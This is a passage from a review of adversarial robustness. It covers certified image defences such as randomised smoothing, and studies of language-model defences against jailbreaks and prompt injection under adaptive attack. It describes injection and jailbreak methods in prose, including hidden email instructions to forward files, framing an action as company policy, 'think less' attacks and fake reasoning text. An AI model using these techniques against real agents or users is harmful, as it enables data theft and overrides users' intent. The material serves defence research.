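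Real attacks such as PGD are imperfect oracles. For such attackers, Montasser and colleagues prove a weaker guarantee: the trained classifier resists future attacks from the attacker used in training. A stronger attacker may succeed far more often. The proof covers only their own algorithm, and they note that nobody had proved a similar guarantee for standard adversarial training. They also consider a deployed model that learns from each successful attack after someone supplies the correct label. The Littlestone dimension of the class then limits the total number of successful attacks, even if the attacker adapts, as long as some classifier in the class resists that attacker completely.

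### Randomised smoothing

If the developer can state the permitted changes, a guarantee doesn't require searching for attacks. The best-known example is the form of randomised smoothing in *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing* (Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter, 2019). Its threat model limits the total size of the change, measured as the square root of the sum of the squared changes to all pixel values, which range from 0 to 1. An attacker with a limit of 1.0 could change one pixel value by all 255 brightness levels, or 100 pixel values by about 25 levels each.

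The method works as follows:

1. Train a base model *f* on images with added Gaussian noise of standard deviation σ, keeping the usual labels.
2. To classify an image, make many copies, add fresh noise to each, run *f* on all of them and return the most common label. If the vote is too close, return no label.
3. To certify the result, take a much larger sample, 100,000 copies in most of the tests by Cohen and colleagues. From the counts, calculate a lower bound *p*_A on the winning label's true probability and an upper bound *p*_B on the runner-up's.
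4. Calculate the certified radius

$$R=\frac{\sigma}{2}\Big(\Phi^{-1}(p_A)-\Phi^{-1}(p_B)\Big)$$

The function Φ⁻¹ converts a probability into a number of standard deviations on the bell curve, so that 0.5 becomes 0, 0.9 becomes 1.28 and 0.1 becomes −1.28. If σ is 0.5, *p*_A is 0.9 and *p*_B is 0.1, the radius is 0.25 × (1.28 + 1.28), or about 0.64, and no smaller change to the input can alter the smoothed classifier's label. For the same σ, the radius would be 1.16 with a vote of 99% to 1% and 0.13 with a vote of 60% to 40%.

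As Montasser and colleagues note, the designer picks the noise to suit the permitted changes, and Gaussian noise suits a limit on total size.

The guarantee comes from the vote rather than the training. When Goodfellow and colleagues only trained networks on noisy digits, the networks were almost as easy to fool as before. In *May the Noise be with you*, Arous, López-Lopera and colleagues (2023) put the noise inside the network during training and removed it for deployment. They report robustness similar to that of adversarial training, without needing a vote at run time. But they measured it against particular attacks and have no certificate, so their result is the same kind of evidence as the test results of the image defences that later failed.

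### Why an adaptive attacker can't beat the certificate

The noisy copies of an image form a cloud around it. An attacker who shifts the image by δ shifts the whole cloud by δ, but can't change *f*'s output at any point. If the shift is small compared with the noise, the old and new clouds overlap heavily, so most of the votes must stay the same.

Cohen and colleagues work out exactly how many votes an attacker can change. Take the case of two labels, and suppose the defender knows only that *f* gives the right label to 90% of the original cloud. Of all the models that fit this description, which one loses the most votes after the shift? The answer is a model with a flat boundary at right angles to the shift, which puts all of the wrong 10% on the side the attacker is heading for. The right label's share of the vote then falls to

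$$\Phi\!\left(\Phi^{-1}(p_A)-\frac{\lVert\delta\rVert}{\sigma}\right)$$

where Φ converts standard deviations back into a probability. For σ = 0.5 this gives:

| Size of the attacker's change | Smallest possible share for the right label |
|---|---|
| 0 | 90% |
| 0.25 | 78% |
| 0.50 | 61% |
| 0.64 | 50% |
| 0.80 | 38% |

Any other base model loses fewer votes, so the right label keeps its majority against every change below the radius of 0.64. This holds even if the attacker knows the weights, the noise level and the whole procedure, and has unlimited computing power. BPDA, label-only searches and transfer attacks are all ways of finding a harmful change, and none exists inside the radius. *Should We Pay This Much for Robustness?* (2026) adds that the bounds hold whatever the model's architecture. Nobody can certify a larger radius from the vote alone, because beyond this one the attacker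 can always beat some base model with the same vote.

The random numbers do have to stay secret. The theorem concerns the true probabilities, but a deployed system estimates them from a finite sample of noisy copies. An attacker who could predict the random numbers could tailor a change to those particular copies. Drawing fresh random numbers for every input prevents this.

Sampling also weakens the guarantee slightly. Cohen and colleagues accepted a 0.1% chance that a certificate would be wrong, and an attacker can bring the vote close to a tie without leaving the certified radius, which often forces the system to return no label. That is less harmful than a wrong label, but it could disable a service. Close votes are uncommon on ordinary pictures. One ImageNet model returned no label for 12% of them with 100 copies and for 1% with 10,000.

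### Certified accuracy on ImageNet

*Certified accuracy* is the share of test images that a model classifies correctly with a certified radius at least as large as the attacker's limit. Apart from the small chance of a wrong certificate, robust accuracy against any attack within that limit is at least as high as certified accuracy. The first models by Cohen and colleagues reached a certified accuracy of 49% at a radius of 0.5 and 12% at 3.0. The model for the smaller radius classified 67% of unaltered images correctly, and the model for the larger radius 44%.

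The base model limits these results because it has to recognise objects through heavy noise. *(Certified!!) Adversarial Robustness for Free!* (Carlini, Tramèr and colleagues, 2022) first removes the noise with a pretrained image-generating diffusion model, then labels the cleaned image with an ordinary pretrained classifier. The certificate still applies because the theorem assumes nothing about *f*, so the denoiser and classifier together can count as the base model. DiffPure also combines a diffusion model with a classifier, but it provides no certificate.

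Carlini and colleagues run the diffusion model only once per copy. The usual procedure takes many small steps, each adding a little new noise. It gives sharper pictures but adds details that weren't in the original, and may turn the object into something else. A single step gives a blurry picture that is more faithful to the original, and the classifier classifies it more accurately.

### What an attacker signal adds

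In 2019, Salman and colleagues proposed SmoothAdv, which combines smoothing with adversarial training. During training, it searches for changes to images that lower the smoothed classifier's vote for the right label, then trains the base model on noisy copies of the altered images. MACER, a method from 2020, instead trains the model to enlarge its certified radius directly, without any attacks.

| Method | Attack search in training | 0.5 | 1.0 | 1.5 | 2.0 | 3.0 |
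|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Training on noise | no | 49% | 37% | 29% | 19% | 12% |
| MACER | no | 57% | 43% | 31% | 25% | 14% |
| SmoothAdv | yes | 56% | 45% | 37% | 27% | 20% |
| Ready-made denoiser and classifier | no | 71.1% | 54.3% | 38.1% | 29.5% | 13.1% |

The table gives certified accuracy on ImageNet at five radii. The figures come from the comparison by Carlini and colleagues, except for SmoothAdv's 45%, which is from *Confidence-aware Denoised Fine-tuning of Off-the-shelf Models for Certified Robustness* (2024).

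Adversarial training adds 7 or 8 percentage points to plain smoothing at every radius. MACER matches that gain at a radius of 0.5 without using attacks, but falls 6 points behind SmoothAdv at 1.5 and 3.0. The ready-made models beat SmoothAdv by 15 points at the smallest radius and lose to it by 7 at the largest, though part of their lead comes from bigger networks and additional training data. The comparison is somewhat fairer on CIFAR-10, because Carlini and colleagues also tested a version there without additional data, after briefly fine-tuning the classifier on denoised images. That version reached 63.8% at a radius of 0.5, against 57.6% for SmoothAdv, and 36.4% at 1.0, against 38.3%. Training against simulated attacks thus seems to help most at large radii, and better denoising at small ones.

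Training against a simulated attack is less risky in SmoothAdv than in ordinary adversarial training, where a weak attack can give a false impression of robustness. A weak attack may lower SmoothAdv's certified accuracy, but it can't produce a false certificate, because the theorem holds for any base model, however it was trained.

Researchers have since improved both approaches. In *Robust Representation Consistency Model via Contrastive Denoising*, Lei, Berner and colleagues (2025) train a single network to recognise a picture at many noise levels, without searching for attacks, so that it doesn't need a separate denoiser. On ImageNet, its certified accuracy is 5.3% higher on average than that of Carlini and colleagues' ready-made models, and up to 11.6% higher at larger radii, and it uses about 1/85 of the computation at run time. Accuracy was still rising as they made the model and the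 training batches larger.

In *Robustifying Diffusion-Denoised Smoothing Against Covariate Shift*, Hedayatnia, Tavassolipour and colleagues (2025) reintroduce an adversarial search into training. A denoiser never estimates the noise perfectly, so the cleaned image differs slightly from anything the classifier saw in training. They start from random noise, use a method like PGD to find the noise that most confuses the classifier after denoising, and train the classifier on the resulting images. This significantly raised certified accuracy on handwritten digits, CIFAR-10 and ImageNet, to what they report as the best results so far. They are still searching for inputs that make the model fail, though this isn't quite a simulated attacker because they search over the noise rather than over changes to the image.

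### Guarantees from interval bounds

Interval-bound training, which Gowal and colleagues proposed in 2018, also uses the permitted changes without searching them for an attack. It replaces each pixel with the range of values the attacker could give it, then calculates the range of values each unit in the network could output. If *a* can lie between 0.4 and 0.6 and *b* between 0.1 and 0.3, a unit that computes 2*a* − *b* must output a value between 0.5 and 1.1. At the last layer, the right label is safe if its lowest possible score is above every other label's highest possible score. Training adjusts the weights to reduce the loss at the worst scores the ranges allow.

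This guarantee doesn't depend on random samples or a vote, and checking an image takes little computation. But the ranges are often too wide. If two units both output *a* and a third subtracts one from the other, the true result is always 0, but the method allows anything from −0.2 to 0.2 because it doesn't track that the two values are equal. These errors build up over many layers. To keep the ranges narrow, training has to favour simple networks, which are often less accurate. According to Cohen and colleagues, no method that carries bounds through a network this way had worked on ImageNet by 2019, while smoothing had.

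### Small radii, high cost and narrow threat models

Certified radii are small compared with ordinary attacks. An ImageNet picture at the usual resolution has 150,528 pixel values, so a total change of 1.0 spread evenly over them moves each by about two thirds of one brightness level. The transfer attacks in Fenaux and colleagues' tests could move every value by 4 levels, a total change of about 6.1. That is twice the largest radius in the table, at which the best figure is only 20%.

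More noise gives larger certified radii but makes the pictures harder to recognise. Cohen and colleagues point out that high-resolution pictures stay recognisable under more noise, which helps somewhat. The number of samples also limits the radius. Even if all 100,000 noisy copies get the same label, the certified radius is only about four times σ.

Certification is also slow. It took Cohen and colleagues 110 seconds per ImageNet picture, and *RRISE* (2026) gives a figure of over 1,500 hours on a graphics processor for all 50,000 test pictures. Lei and colleagues measured 52 minutes for a single picture with one diffusion-based method. A prediction without a certificate takes 0.15 seconds with 100 copies. *RRISE* trains a second network to predict the outcome of the vote and calibrates its predictions on a separate set of images. This makes certificates much faster to produce, but the resulting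 guarantee holds only for most images from the same source, and an attacker can choose unusual ones.

The certificate gives no protection outside the stated threat model. *Position* (2025), a paper arguing that certified robustness is not yet security, says smoothing's guarantees cover additive changes. A slight rotation or a sticker can be a large change by that measure, even if a person would hardly care about it. A certificate also shows only that a label is stable, not that it is correct. If an attacker moves an image well beyond the radius, the system receives only the altered image and may certify the wrong label around it.

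The problem remains open for deployed systems. After attacking commercial systems, Zhang and colleagues call visual robustness "still largely unsolved". They add that training a model to refuse harmful requests doesn't help, because the model's answer matches the picture it perceives.

### Can any finite set of guardrails be complete?

Language models have no obvious equivalent of a small radius, since an attacker can write anything. Many systems rely on guardrails, which are rules and filters meant to stop them from producing forbidden content. In 2026, Apostol Vassilev, the first author of the NIST taxonomy of attacks, proved that for any finite set of guardrails, some prompt will make the AI system disregard them, according to Help Net Security's *Every set of AI guardrails can be broken by the right prompt*.

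The proof builds on Kurt Gödel's incompleteness theorems of 1931. Gödel showed that any consistent theory that has a finite list of axioms and can express arithmetic leaves some true statements unproved. Adding those statements as axioms creates a larger theory with new gaps. Vassilev treats guardrails the same way, as a finite set of rules for judging an unlimited range of text, and argues that each new rule leaves other prompts uncovered.

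The result depends on what counts as a guardrail. A system that answers every prompt with the same refusal follows a finite rule that nobody can evade, so the theorem must concern systems that stay useful and have to interpret open-ended text. It also applies less obviously to restrictions on what a system can do, such as those that protect some agents from prompt injection. A program with no way to send email can't send any, whatever the prompt. The theorem doesn't conflict with randomised smoothing, which guarantees only that one label will stay the same under one limited kind of change.

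The proof applies to any finite set of guardrails, whether the developer wrote them without seeing an attack or derived them from a million successful jailbreaks. It doesn't show how to find the prompt that defeats the guardrails or estimate how long the search would take. A guardrail is incomplete in this sense whether breaking it would take ten minutes or years.

Vassilev's practical advice does favour attacker signals. He wants red teams to look for new prompts continually, developers to update the guardrails after each discovery, and organisations to prepare to limit the damage when an attack succeeds. The updated guardrails are still a finite set, so the theorem applies to them too. The aim is to make the next successful prompt take more effort to find than attackers can put in, and experiments are needed to test whether a defence achieves that.

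## Do language-model defences built without attack examples hold?

A developer who has collected no attacks on a language model can make the model larger, let it reason for longer before it answers, or word its prompt so that it gives less weight to instructions from strangers. Developers already use larger models and longer reasoning to improve ordinary performance, so if either were enough for robustness, they would get robustness as a by-product.

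### Larger models

FAR.AI, an AI safety research non-profit, tested how model size affects robustness using Pythia, a family of open models with similar designs and the same training data. It trained models of each size to classify text, for example as spam or not, and then attacked them by adding ten tokens (words or pieces of words) to the end of the text. It chose the tokens with GCG, the gradient-guided search that other researchers used on the malware detector. FAR.AI's first account, *Does Robustness Improve with Scale?*, reports that larger models tended to be more robust, but that chance differences in training could outweigh a doubling of size and sometimes a tenfold increase.

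The full study, *Scaling Trends in Language Model Robustness* (Howe, McKenzie and colleagues, 2024), tested Pythia models with 7.6 million to 11.6 billion parameters (weights) and added a newer family, Qwen2.5. On film reviews, GCG fooled the smallest Pythia model almost every time and the largest less than 20% of the time. On spam, it succeeded more often against a model with 6.7 billion parameters than against one about a fiftieth of that size. When the task was to pick the longer of two words, size made no difference. Larger Qwen2.5 chat models refused harmful requests under attack more often than smaller ones, but those models had also received safety training, which Howe and colleagues think explains the trend.

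Adversarial training made a larger and more reliable difference. On several tasks, five rounds of attacking and retraining cut the attack success rate from above 90% to below 20%. On the spam task, adversarial training with only 0.001% as much computing as the Pythia models' original training cut the success rate of an attack of a given strength from 50% to below 10%. At every model size that Howe and colleagues studied, doubling both sides' computing still favoured attackers. This advantage shrank as models grew, so attacking very large models with adversarial training might eventually take more computing than defending them.

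Newer comparisons of released models don't show a consistent benefit from size either. *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark of prompt injection against agents, found that the larger model was harder to attack in the Llama and Gemma families, but in Qwen2.5 the attack success rate rose from 20.9% with 14 billion parameters to 25.7% with 32 billion. *JailBound* (2026), a study of jailbreaks, found that in three families a middle-sized model was easier to attack than both smaller and larger ones.

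The company Gray Swan AI has run public competitions in which people attack agents for prize money. *Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* (2025) describes one in which almost 2,000 people made about 1.8 million attempts on 22 models. GPT-4.5 was about ten times as large as GPT-4o but not correspondingly more robust. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) compared 13 models' results in a later competition with their scores on GPQA Diamond, a test of difficult science questions. More capable models were slightly harder to attack, but with only 13 models the correlation of −0.31 could easily be chance. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Kimi K2 both scored about 85% on the test, yet attacks succeeded 8.5% of the time against Gemini and 4.8% against Kimi.

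None of these comparisons isolates the effect of size, because developers also give their models different safety training. Within the Claude 4.5 family, the attack success rate fell from 1.3% for the least capable model to 0.5% for the most capable. But Dziemian and colleagues think that, across all 13 models, a family's training matters more than its capability.

### More reasoning before the answer

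Reasoning models write out intermediate steps before they answer, which gives them more chances to check an instruction against the rules in their prompt. Zaremba, Nitishinskaya and colleagues at OpenAI tested whether more reasoning makes two such models, o1-preview and o1-mini, robust (*Trading Inference-Time Compute for Adversarial Robustness*, 2025). They did no adversarial training for the tasks they studied and changed only the amount of reasoning, using the same setting that improves the models' ordinary performance. The extra reasoning involved no simulated attacker, but both models had already had safety training, which may have used simulated attacks.

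In a typical test, the prompt contained an instruction to solve a maths problem and ignore everything between two markers. The attacker controlled the text between the markers and tried to make the model give a particular wrong answer, such as the right answer plus one. One attack filled the space with many worked examples containing the desired mistake. In another, a second language model generated new attempts up to 25 times, using information about those that had failed. A white-box attack used gradients to optimise the vectors that represent the text inside the model.

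For any fixed number of worked examples, the attack's success rate approached zero as reasoning increased. It sometimes rose at first, apparently because a model with very little reasoning couldn't follow the attacker's pattern. Instructions hidden in web pages also stopped working in most settings. Reasoning helped against the optimised vectors on nearly every task, but an attacker who could use enough of them still succeeded often.

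Forty human attackers also tried to make o1-preview break OpenAI's content rules, without knowing how much reasoning it was using. They found 20 successful prompts at each of five reasoning levels, and the researchers then tried each prompt at the other four levels.

| | Level 1 (least reasoning) | Level 2 | Level 3 | Level 4 | Level 5 (most reasoning) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Average attempts per successful attack | 11.0 | 16.8 | 15.6 | 15.9 | 22.6 |
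| Success rate of prompts found at other levels | 36% | 30% | 21% | 20% | 19% |

The highest level took about twice as many attempts as the lowest, while the three in between hardly differed. Even the 23 attempts needed at the highest level are not much work for a determined attacker.

Reasoning helped little when the rules were ambiguous. The automated attacker could take a request for harmful advice, remove the signs of bad intent, and get relevant information within a few attempts, however much the model reasoned. Zaremba and colleagues attribute this to their automated grader, which marked as harmful some answers that OpenAI's rules allowed. They compare the model to a judge, who may apply a clear law better with more time but can't close loopholes in the law.

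Attackers can also target the reasoning itself. Zaremba and colleagues found a "think less" attack that gets the model to cut its reasoning short. It worked well against o1-mini and less well against o1-preview, and developers can watch for it by flagging unusually short reasoning. At all but the lowest reasoning level, attacks also succeeded more often on the 5% of cases with the most reasoning than on typical cases. The researchers suspect that the model gets stuck in unproductive loops, and that attackers could learn to cause them.

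Wu, Xiang and colleagues (2025), in *Does More Inference-Time Compute Really Help Robustness?*, found similar gains in 12 open models. They controlled the length of the reasoning by cutting it off at a limit or prompting the model to continue. When they raised the limit from 100 to 16,000 tokens, one model, QwQ-32B, went from ignoring about 35% of injected instructions to ignoring about 75%. Refusals of harmful requests hardly changed. Both results come from fixed sets of attacks, so they don't show how much of the gain would remain against an attacker who adapts.

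The gains also depend on keeping the reasoning hidden. Suppose that each token of reasoning has at least a probability *p* of containing something the attacker wants, such as part of a secret key. The probability that this happens somewhere in *L* tokens is then at least

$$1-(1-p)^L$$

If *p* is 1 in 10,000, this is about 1% for 100 tokens and 80% for 16,000. When Wu and colleagues counted any malicious text in the reasoning as a failure, one 14-billion-parameter model's robustness to prompt injection fell from about 90% to below 20% as they raised the limit. They acknowledge that such text isn't always dangerous. It can be dangerous if the reasoning reveals a secret, or if the model acts through tools before it finishes reasoning. Attackers can sometimes reconstruct hidden reasoning.

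Another limit is that extra reasoning helped only a little against altered images. OpenAI's tests included pictures that other researchers had altered to fool Google's Bard. *Get RICH or Die Scaling* (McDonald, Lei and colleagues, 2025) reports that these pictures fooled an OpenAI reasoning model 46% of the time, and still 39% of the time with the most reasoning. McDonald and colleagues argue that a model can apply its rules to an attacked input only if it can still interpret that input correctly, which adversarial training helps it do.

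The researchers tested this on three related models that answer questions about images. The attacker altered a picture to make the model produce a particular sentence, and the researchers recorded the attacker's loss after 300 search steps. A higher loss means the attacker is further from succeeding. They then added an instruction to the prompt telling the model not to let text in the image influence its answer.

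| Adversarial training | Attacker's loss without the instruction | Attacker's loss with the instruction |
|---|---|---|
| None | 2.0 | attack succeeded |
| Some | 7.0 | 7.2 |
| Extensive | 12.4 | 21.1 |

The instruction helped only the model with the most adversarial training. Similarly, in a separate test, a 20-billion-parameter reasoning model gained little from more reasoning until McDonald and colleagues adversarially trained the part that processes images. An attacker-free defence can therefore add to an attack-simulating one but cannot replace it.

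Tests of reasoning against human attackers have given mixed results. *Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* reports a marginal benefit from reasoning for Claude 3.7 Sonnet and a negligible one for o3-mini. When Dziemian and colleagues tried a collection of successful attacks on Kimi K2, 35% worked without reasoning and 30% with it. Nasr and colleagues held a competition in which people attacked Gemini 2.5 Flash, with no added defence, on five tasks. Turning reasoning on lowered the attackers' success rate on two tasks and raised it on three.

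Attackers can also plant text that imitates the model's own reasoning. This was the most successful of 27 strategies in the competition that Dziemian and colleagues studied, although most of the models had reasoning turned off. In *GPT-Red*, Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues (2026) found that this strategy reliably works on many models. They also found that GPT-5.6, which OpenAI trained on simulated attacks, was more robust than GPT-5.1 when both used a high level of reasoning. Larger models may not resist such attacks better. In *How Well Can Reasoning Models Identify and Recover from Unhelpful Thoughts?* (2025), researchers inserted a harmful question and a short jailbreak into models' reasoning, and the smallest model in each family resisted best.

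### Prompts that separate trusted from untrusted text

Prompt injection works because a language model receives its user's request and the material it reads as one stream of text. Spotlighting uses special markers to separate the trusted text from the rest and tells the model to pay extra attention to the trusted text. Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after the material. If a user asks for a summary of an email that contains a hidden instruction to forward the user's files, the model reads the request for a summary, then the email, then the request again.

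Neither defence requires training, and both do well against attacks that simply tell the model to forget its task. *INFUSE* tested a similar method, which also puts markers around untrusted text, against a fixed set of 20 attacks. With the method, the attacks succeeded less often on all five models tested.

An attacker can get around both defences by presenting the harmful action as part of the user's task. In the email example, the attacker might write in the hidden text that company policy requires the assistant to forward the files before it can summarise anything. Repeating the user's request doesn't help, because a model that treats this as true will forward the files to write the summary. Nasr and colleagues used an automated search to find attacks of this type against Sandwiching.

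### Twelve defences under adaptive attack

*The Attacker Moves Second*, the October 2025 study by Nasr and colleagues, tested these two defences and ten others. All of its attacks repeat the same loop: propose some text, score how well it works, keep the best attempts and use them to write new ones. The attacks fall into four families:

- **Gradient attacks** use the model's gradients to choose which tokens to replace. The researchers used GCG for this and tried it on only one defence, because they consider gradient attacks on text unreliable.
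- **Reinforcement learning** trains a language model to attack. It gets five attempts in each session, sees the target's responses and scores, and has its weights updated after a batch of 32 sessions.
- **Search** uses a language model to rewrite earlier attempts, while another model scores the results from 1 to 10. The program keeps a varied collection of the best attempts and can query the target up to 800 times.
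- **Human attackers** took part in an online competition with more than 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes. They could watch the agent's actions and revise their text.

The table sorts the twelve defences by how much attacker information went into building them. Nasr and colleagues tested eight on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which an agent does office and travel tasks with simulated tools. For these eight, the table gives the success rates of AgentDojo's fixed attack and of the adaptive search. The base model is Gemini 2.5 Pro for all of them except Meta SecAlign, which is itself a model. A dash marks defences they tested on other benchmarks, where AgentDojo's fixed attack doesn't apply.

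| Defence | Attacker information used | Fixed attack | Adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| No added defence | – | 30% | 100% |
| Spotlighting | none | 28% | 99% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | none | 21% | 95% |
| MELON | none | 0% | 89% |
| Protect AI | stored attacks | 15% | 90% |
| PromptGuard | stored attacks | 26% | 94% |
| PIGuard | stored attacks | 0% | 71% |
| Meta SecAlign | stored attacks | 5% | 96% |
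| StruQ | stored attacks | – | 100% |
| Circuit Breakers | disputed | – | 100% |
| RPO | stored and newly generated attacks | – | 96–98% |
| Data Sentinel | search during training | – | all cases |
| Model Armor | not public | 28% | 90% |

MELON is the only other defence in the table that uses no attack examples. It runs the agent twice, the second time replacing the user's request with a request to summarise the material. If the agent takes the same action both times, the instruction for it probably came from the material, so MELON raises an alarm. Attackers beat it with instructions that apply only when the agent isn't summarising. On another base model, Llama 3.3 70B, the search succeeded 76% of the time without information about MELON and 95% of the time with it.

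Protect AI, PromptGuard and PIGuard are filters trained on harmless text and known attacks. A search-based attack got past them with instructions that looked like routine office procedures. RPO adds to the prompt a short text that its designers optimised against a collection of jailbreaks. Gradient-based attacks defeated it 96% of the time, and attacks using reinforcement learning did so 98% of the time.

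Data Sentinel comes closest to adversarial training, because it trains a separate model against attacks that adapt to that model. It prompts the model to repeat a secret word and ignore the text under inspection, and treats a failure to repeat the word as a sign of injection. Nasr and colleagues bypassed it in every case by redefining the task, so searching for attacks during training did not guarantee robustness either.

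### What the success rates show

Nasr and colleagues report that fixed attacks on Spotlighting and Sandwiching succeeded as little as 1% of the time, while their own search succeeded more than 95% of the time. The 1% rate depends on the base model. It was measured with Spotlighting added to Meta SecAlign, which was already trained to resist injections and let through only 5% of the fixed attacks without Spotlighting. With Gemini, the fixed attack succeeded 28% of the time against Spotlighting, almost the same as without it.

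Successful attacks also didn't take noticeably longer to find with the two prompt defences. Against Gemini, they took a median of 14 queries with either defence and 13 without one. Results were more promising on GPT-5 Mini, where the search succeeded 75% of the time without a defence, 69% with Sandwiching and 47% with Spotlighting. This is some evidence that Spotlighting can help a model that is already harder to attack. But the search ran only once per task, and its results varied a lot between runs. Nasr and colleagues expect that a larger budget would raise the success rate on GPT-5 Mini too.

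Human attackers made 265 successful attacks on Spotlighting and 178 on Sandwiching. On the task used to test Spotlighting, their success rate was higher with the defence than without it for four of six models. For Gemini 2.5 Flash, it rose from 28.8% to 43.7%. This doesn't prove that Spotlighting made the model weaker, because participants chose how much effort to put into each challenge. On the 29 combinations of task, model and defence that both people and the search attempted, at least one person succeeded on every combination, while the search succeeded on 69%. The best individual who tried all 29 succeeded on 75%, so much of the human advantage came from having many people try.

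Nasr and colleagues warn that their figures aren't necessarily comparable across defences. They mostly kept each designer's own benchmark and chose the attack they expected to work best. RPO's 98% is the rate at which jailbreaks got harmful content out of a model, while Spotlighting's 99% is the rate at which an agent followed hidden instructions. These figures don't show that optimising a prompt against attacks is no better than writing one without them, or that training on stored attacks adds nothing. Showing either would require testing both kinds of defence on the same base model and tasks, with equal effort from the attacker.

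Even the AgentDojo results don't give a fair ranking of the defences. Adaptive attacks succeeded least often against PIGuard, at 71%, but PIGuard also cut the share of ordinary tasks that the Gemini agent completed from 74% to 39%. A filter that blocks that much harmless text will also block some attacks. The study does show that all twelve defences, including the three built without attack examples, failed against a well-resourced attacker who adapted to them.

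The gap between fixed and adaptive attacks persists in newer models. In *Adaptive Adversaries*, Jain, Hartmann and Li had language models attack agents that ran on models such as Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.4. The attacker's first message succeeded at most 1% of the time. After 15 rounds of adapting to the agent's responses, the success rate, averaged across tasks, was between 8.3% and 19.0%. The agents had no memory of earlier rounds, so they couldn't detect repeated attempts. These rates are much lower than those in the study by Nasr and colleagues, but the tasks and attackers also differed. Success rates varied widely between tasks, and on one task attacks succeeded 60% of the time against Claude and 7% against GPT-5.4.

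### The dispute over Circuit Breakers

Andy Zou, Long Phan and colleagues proposed Circuit Breakers in 2024 as an alternative to adversarial training. Each layer of a language model turns text into long lists of numbers, called internal representations. Circuit Breakers retrains the model on examples of harmful answers, pushing their representations away from the directions they had in the original model so that the model can't continue the answer. On harmless examples, the training keeps the representations close to the original ones so that the model stays useful.

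The designers argue that this protection should work even against jailbreaks nobody has seen yet. Whatever the jailbreak, the model must represent harmful content internally before it can write it, so redirecting those representations should stop the attack.

Nasr and colleagues instead group Circuit Breakers with StruQ and Meta SecAlign, saying that its designers also generated adversarial examples and trained on them. The disagreement is partly about what counts as an attack example. A harmful answer shows what a failure looks like, but not which prompt would cause it. Training only on plain harmful requests and their answers would use no attacker signal if the original model refuses those requests. Adding jailbreak prompts that had worked on the model would make the defence one that simulates an attacker.

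Circuit Breakers failed, however one classifies it. The reinforcement-learning attack succeeded 100% of the time on HarmBench, a standard set of harmful requests. The attacker could see the probability the model assigned to the harmful text, which an ordinary chatbot user can't, so the result doesn't show how quickly such a user would succeed. But it undermines the claim that the defence works independently of particular attacks, because the model must still have been able to produce harmful answers through representations that its training had not redirected.

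## What does training against a simulated attacker add for language models?

StruQ and Meta SecAlign learn from a fixed list of attack templates, and adaptive attacks nearly always beat them in the tests by Nasr and colleagues. Using a fixed list is the way to simulate an attacker that needs the least computing. Developers can also search for harmful changes to the numbers inside the model, or train a second model to attack the first. The question is how much protection the extra computing for these methods adds.

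### Fixed injection templates

StruQ and Meta SecAlign start from ordinary examples of a model following an instruction about some text. The developer inserts a second instruction into the text, using a template such as one that makes the user's task look finished. The model then learns to answer as if the inserted instruction were not there.

StruQ uses reserved markers to separate the user's instruction from the text, and trains the model to give the right answer anyway. If *x*′ is the prompt with the injection and *y*ᵤ the answer to the user's real request, training lowers

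$$L_{\text{StruQ}}=-\log \pi(y_u\mid x')$$

where π is the probability the model gives to an answer. Meta SecAlign also uses the answer the attacker wants, *y*ₐ, and trains the model to prefer one over the other:

$$L_{\text{SecAlign}}=-\log\sigma\!\left(\beta\log\frac{\pi(y_u\mid x')}{\pi_0(y_u\mid x')}-\beta\log\frac{\pi(y_a\mid x')}{\pi_0(y_a\mid x')}\right)$$

Here π₀ is the model before this training, σ is the logistic function and β sets how strongly the preference counts. Suppose the user wants a summary of a hotel review, and the review contains an instruction to print a certain word. Then *y*ᵤ is the summary and *y*ₐ is the word. The loss falls as the summary becomes more likely relative to the word.

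Templates do give some protection. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested Meta SecAlign's method on the small open model Qwen3-4B, using the AgentDojo benchmark. The method cut the average success rate of five fixed attacks from 33.3% to 3.5%, and that of six adaptive attacks from 32.1% to 12.5%. The adaptive attacks ran on only 40 tasks, chosen because the undefended model was vulnerable on them.

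### Changes to embeddings and activations

A language model first converts each token into a list of numbers, called an embedding. The internal representations that its layers then compute are also called activations. Continuous adversarial training lets the simulated attacker change the embeddings directly, without looking for words that would produce the change. For a harmful request *x* with embeddings *e*(*x*) and a refusal *y*, the aim has the same form as Mądry and colleagues' formula for images:

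$$\min_\theta\;\mathbb{E}_{(x,y)}\Big[\max_{\lVert\delta\rVert\le\varepsilon}L(\theta,\,e(x)+\delta,\,y)\Big]$$

The inner search takes a few gradient steps, as PGD does, towards the small change δ that makes a refusal least likely. The outer step trains the model to refuse anyway. Developers also train on harmless requests so the model doesn't learn to refuse everything. Latent adversarial training works the same way but adds δ to the activations in a later layer.

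Attacking the embeddings takes less compute than attacking the text of a request because the attacker searches over numbers instead of words. In Llama 3.1 8B, each embedding has 4,096 numbers, so a 20-token request gives the attacker 81,920 numbers to adjust, and a single gradient calculation shows which way to move all of them. An attack on the text has to choose among about 128,000 tokens for each position and test many candidates.

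Neither method needs a collection of jailbreaks, but both are attack-simulating because they search for failures of the current model in every batch. Their threat model is weak because most of the altered embeddings correspond to no text anyone could type, while a real jailbreak may rewrite the whole request and move the embeddings much further than ε. The developer relies on robustness to small numerical changes carrying over to large changes of wording. Casper and colleagues, who used latent adversarial training for this purpose in 2024, gave a reason to expect some carry-over: later layers represent concepts more than exact words, so one change there may correspond to many different prompts.

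### Training an attacker and a defender together

In joint training, a language model plays the attacker and learns from its successes while the defender learns from its failures. Self-RedTeam, AdvGame, MAGIC and AdvGRPO all use this method. MAGIC and AdvGame use separate models for the two roles, and MAGIC trains them in turns.

Wang, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentSafeEvo*, extended the idea to agents. Both their attacker and their defender start from Qwen3-8B. The attacker first studies about 10,000 adversarial tasks and 10,000 harmless ones, because an untrained model can't reliably write a usable task. The joint training then repeats this loop:

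1. The attacker receives a setting, an intention and some information about the environment. It writes several complete tasks, each with a user's request, a set of tools and the material that the tools will return. It can put the attack in any of these.
2. The defender attempts each task several times, calling tools over many turns.
3. A larger model judges every attempt on two points. Safety earns +1 if the attempt was safe and −1 if not. Usefulness earns +1 if the defender did the legitimate part of the task and −1 if not. If the whole request is harmful, a refusal counts as useful.
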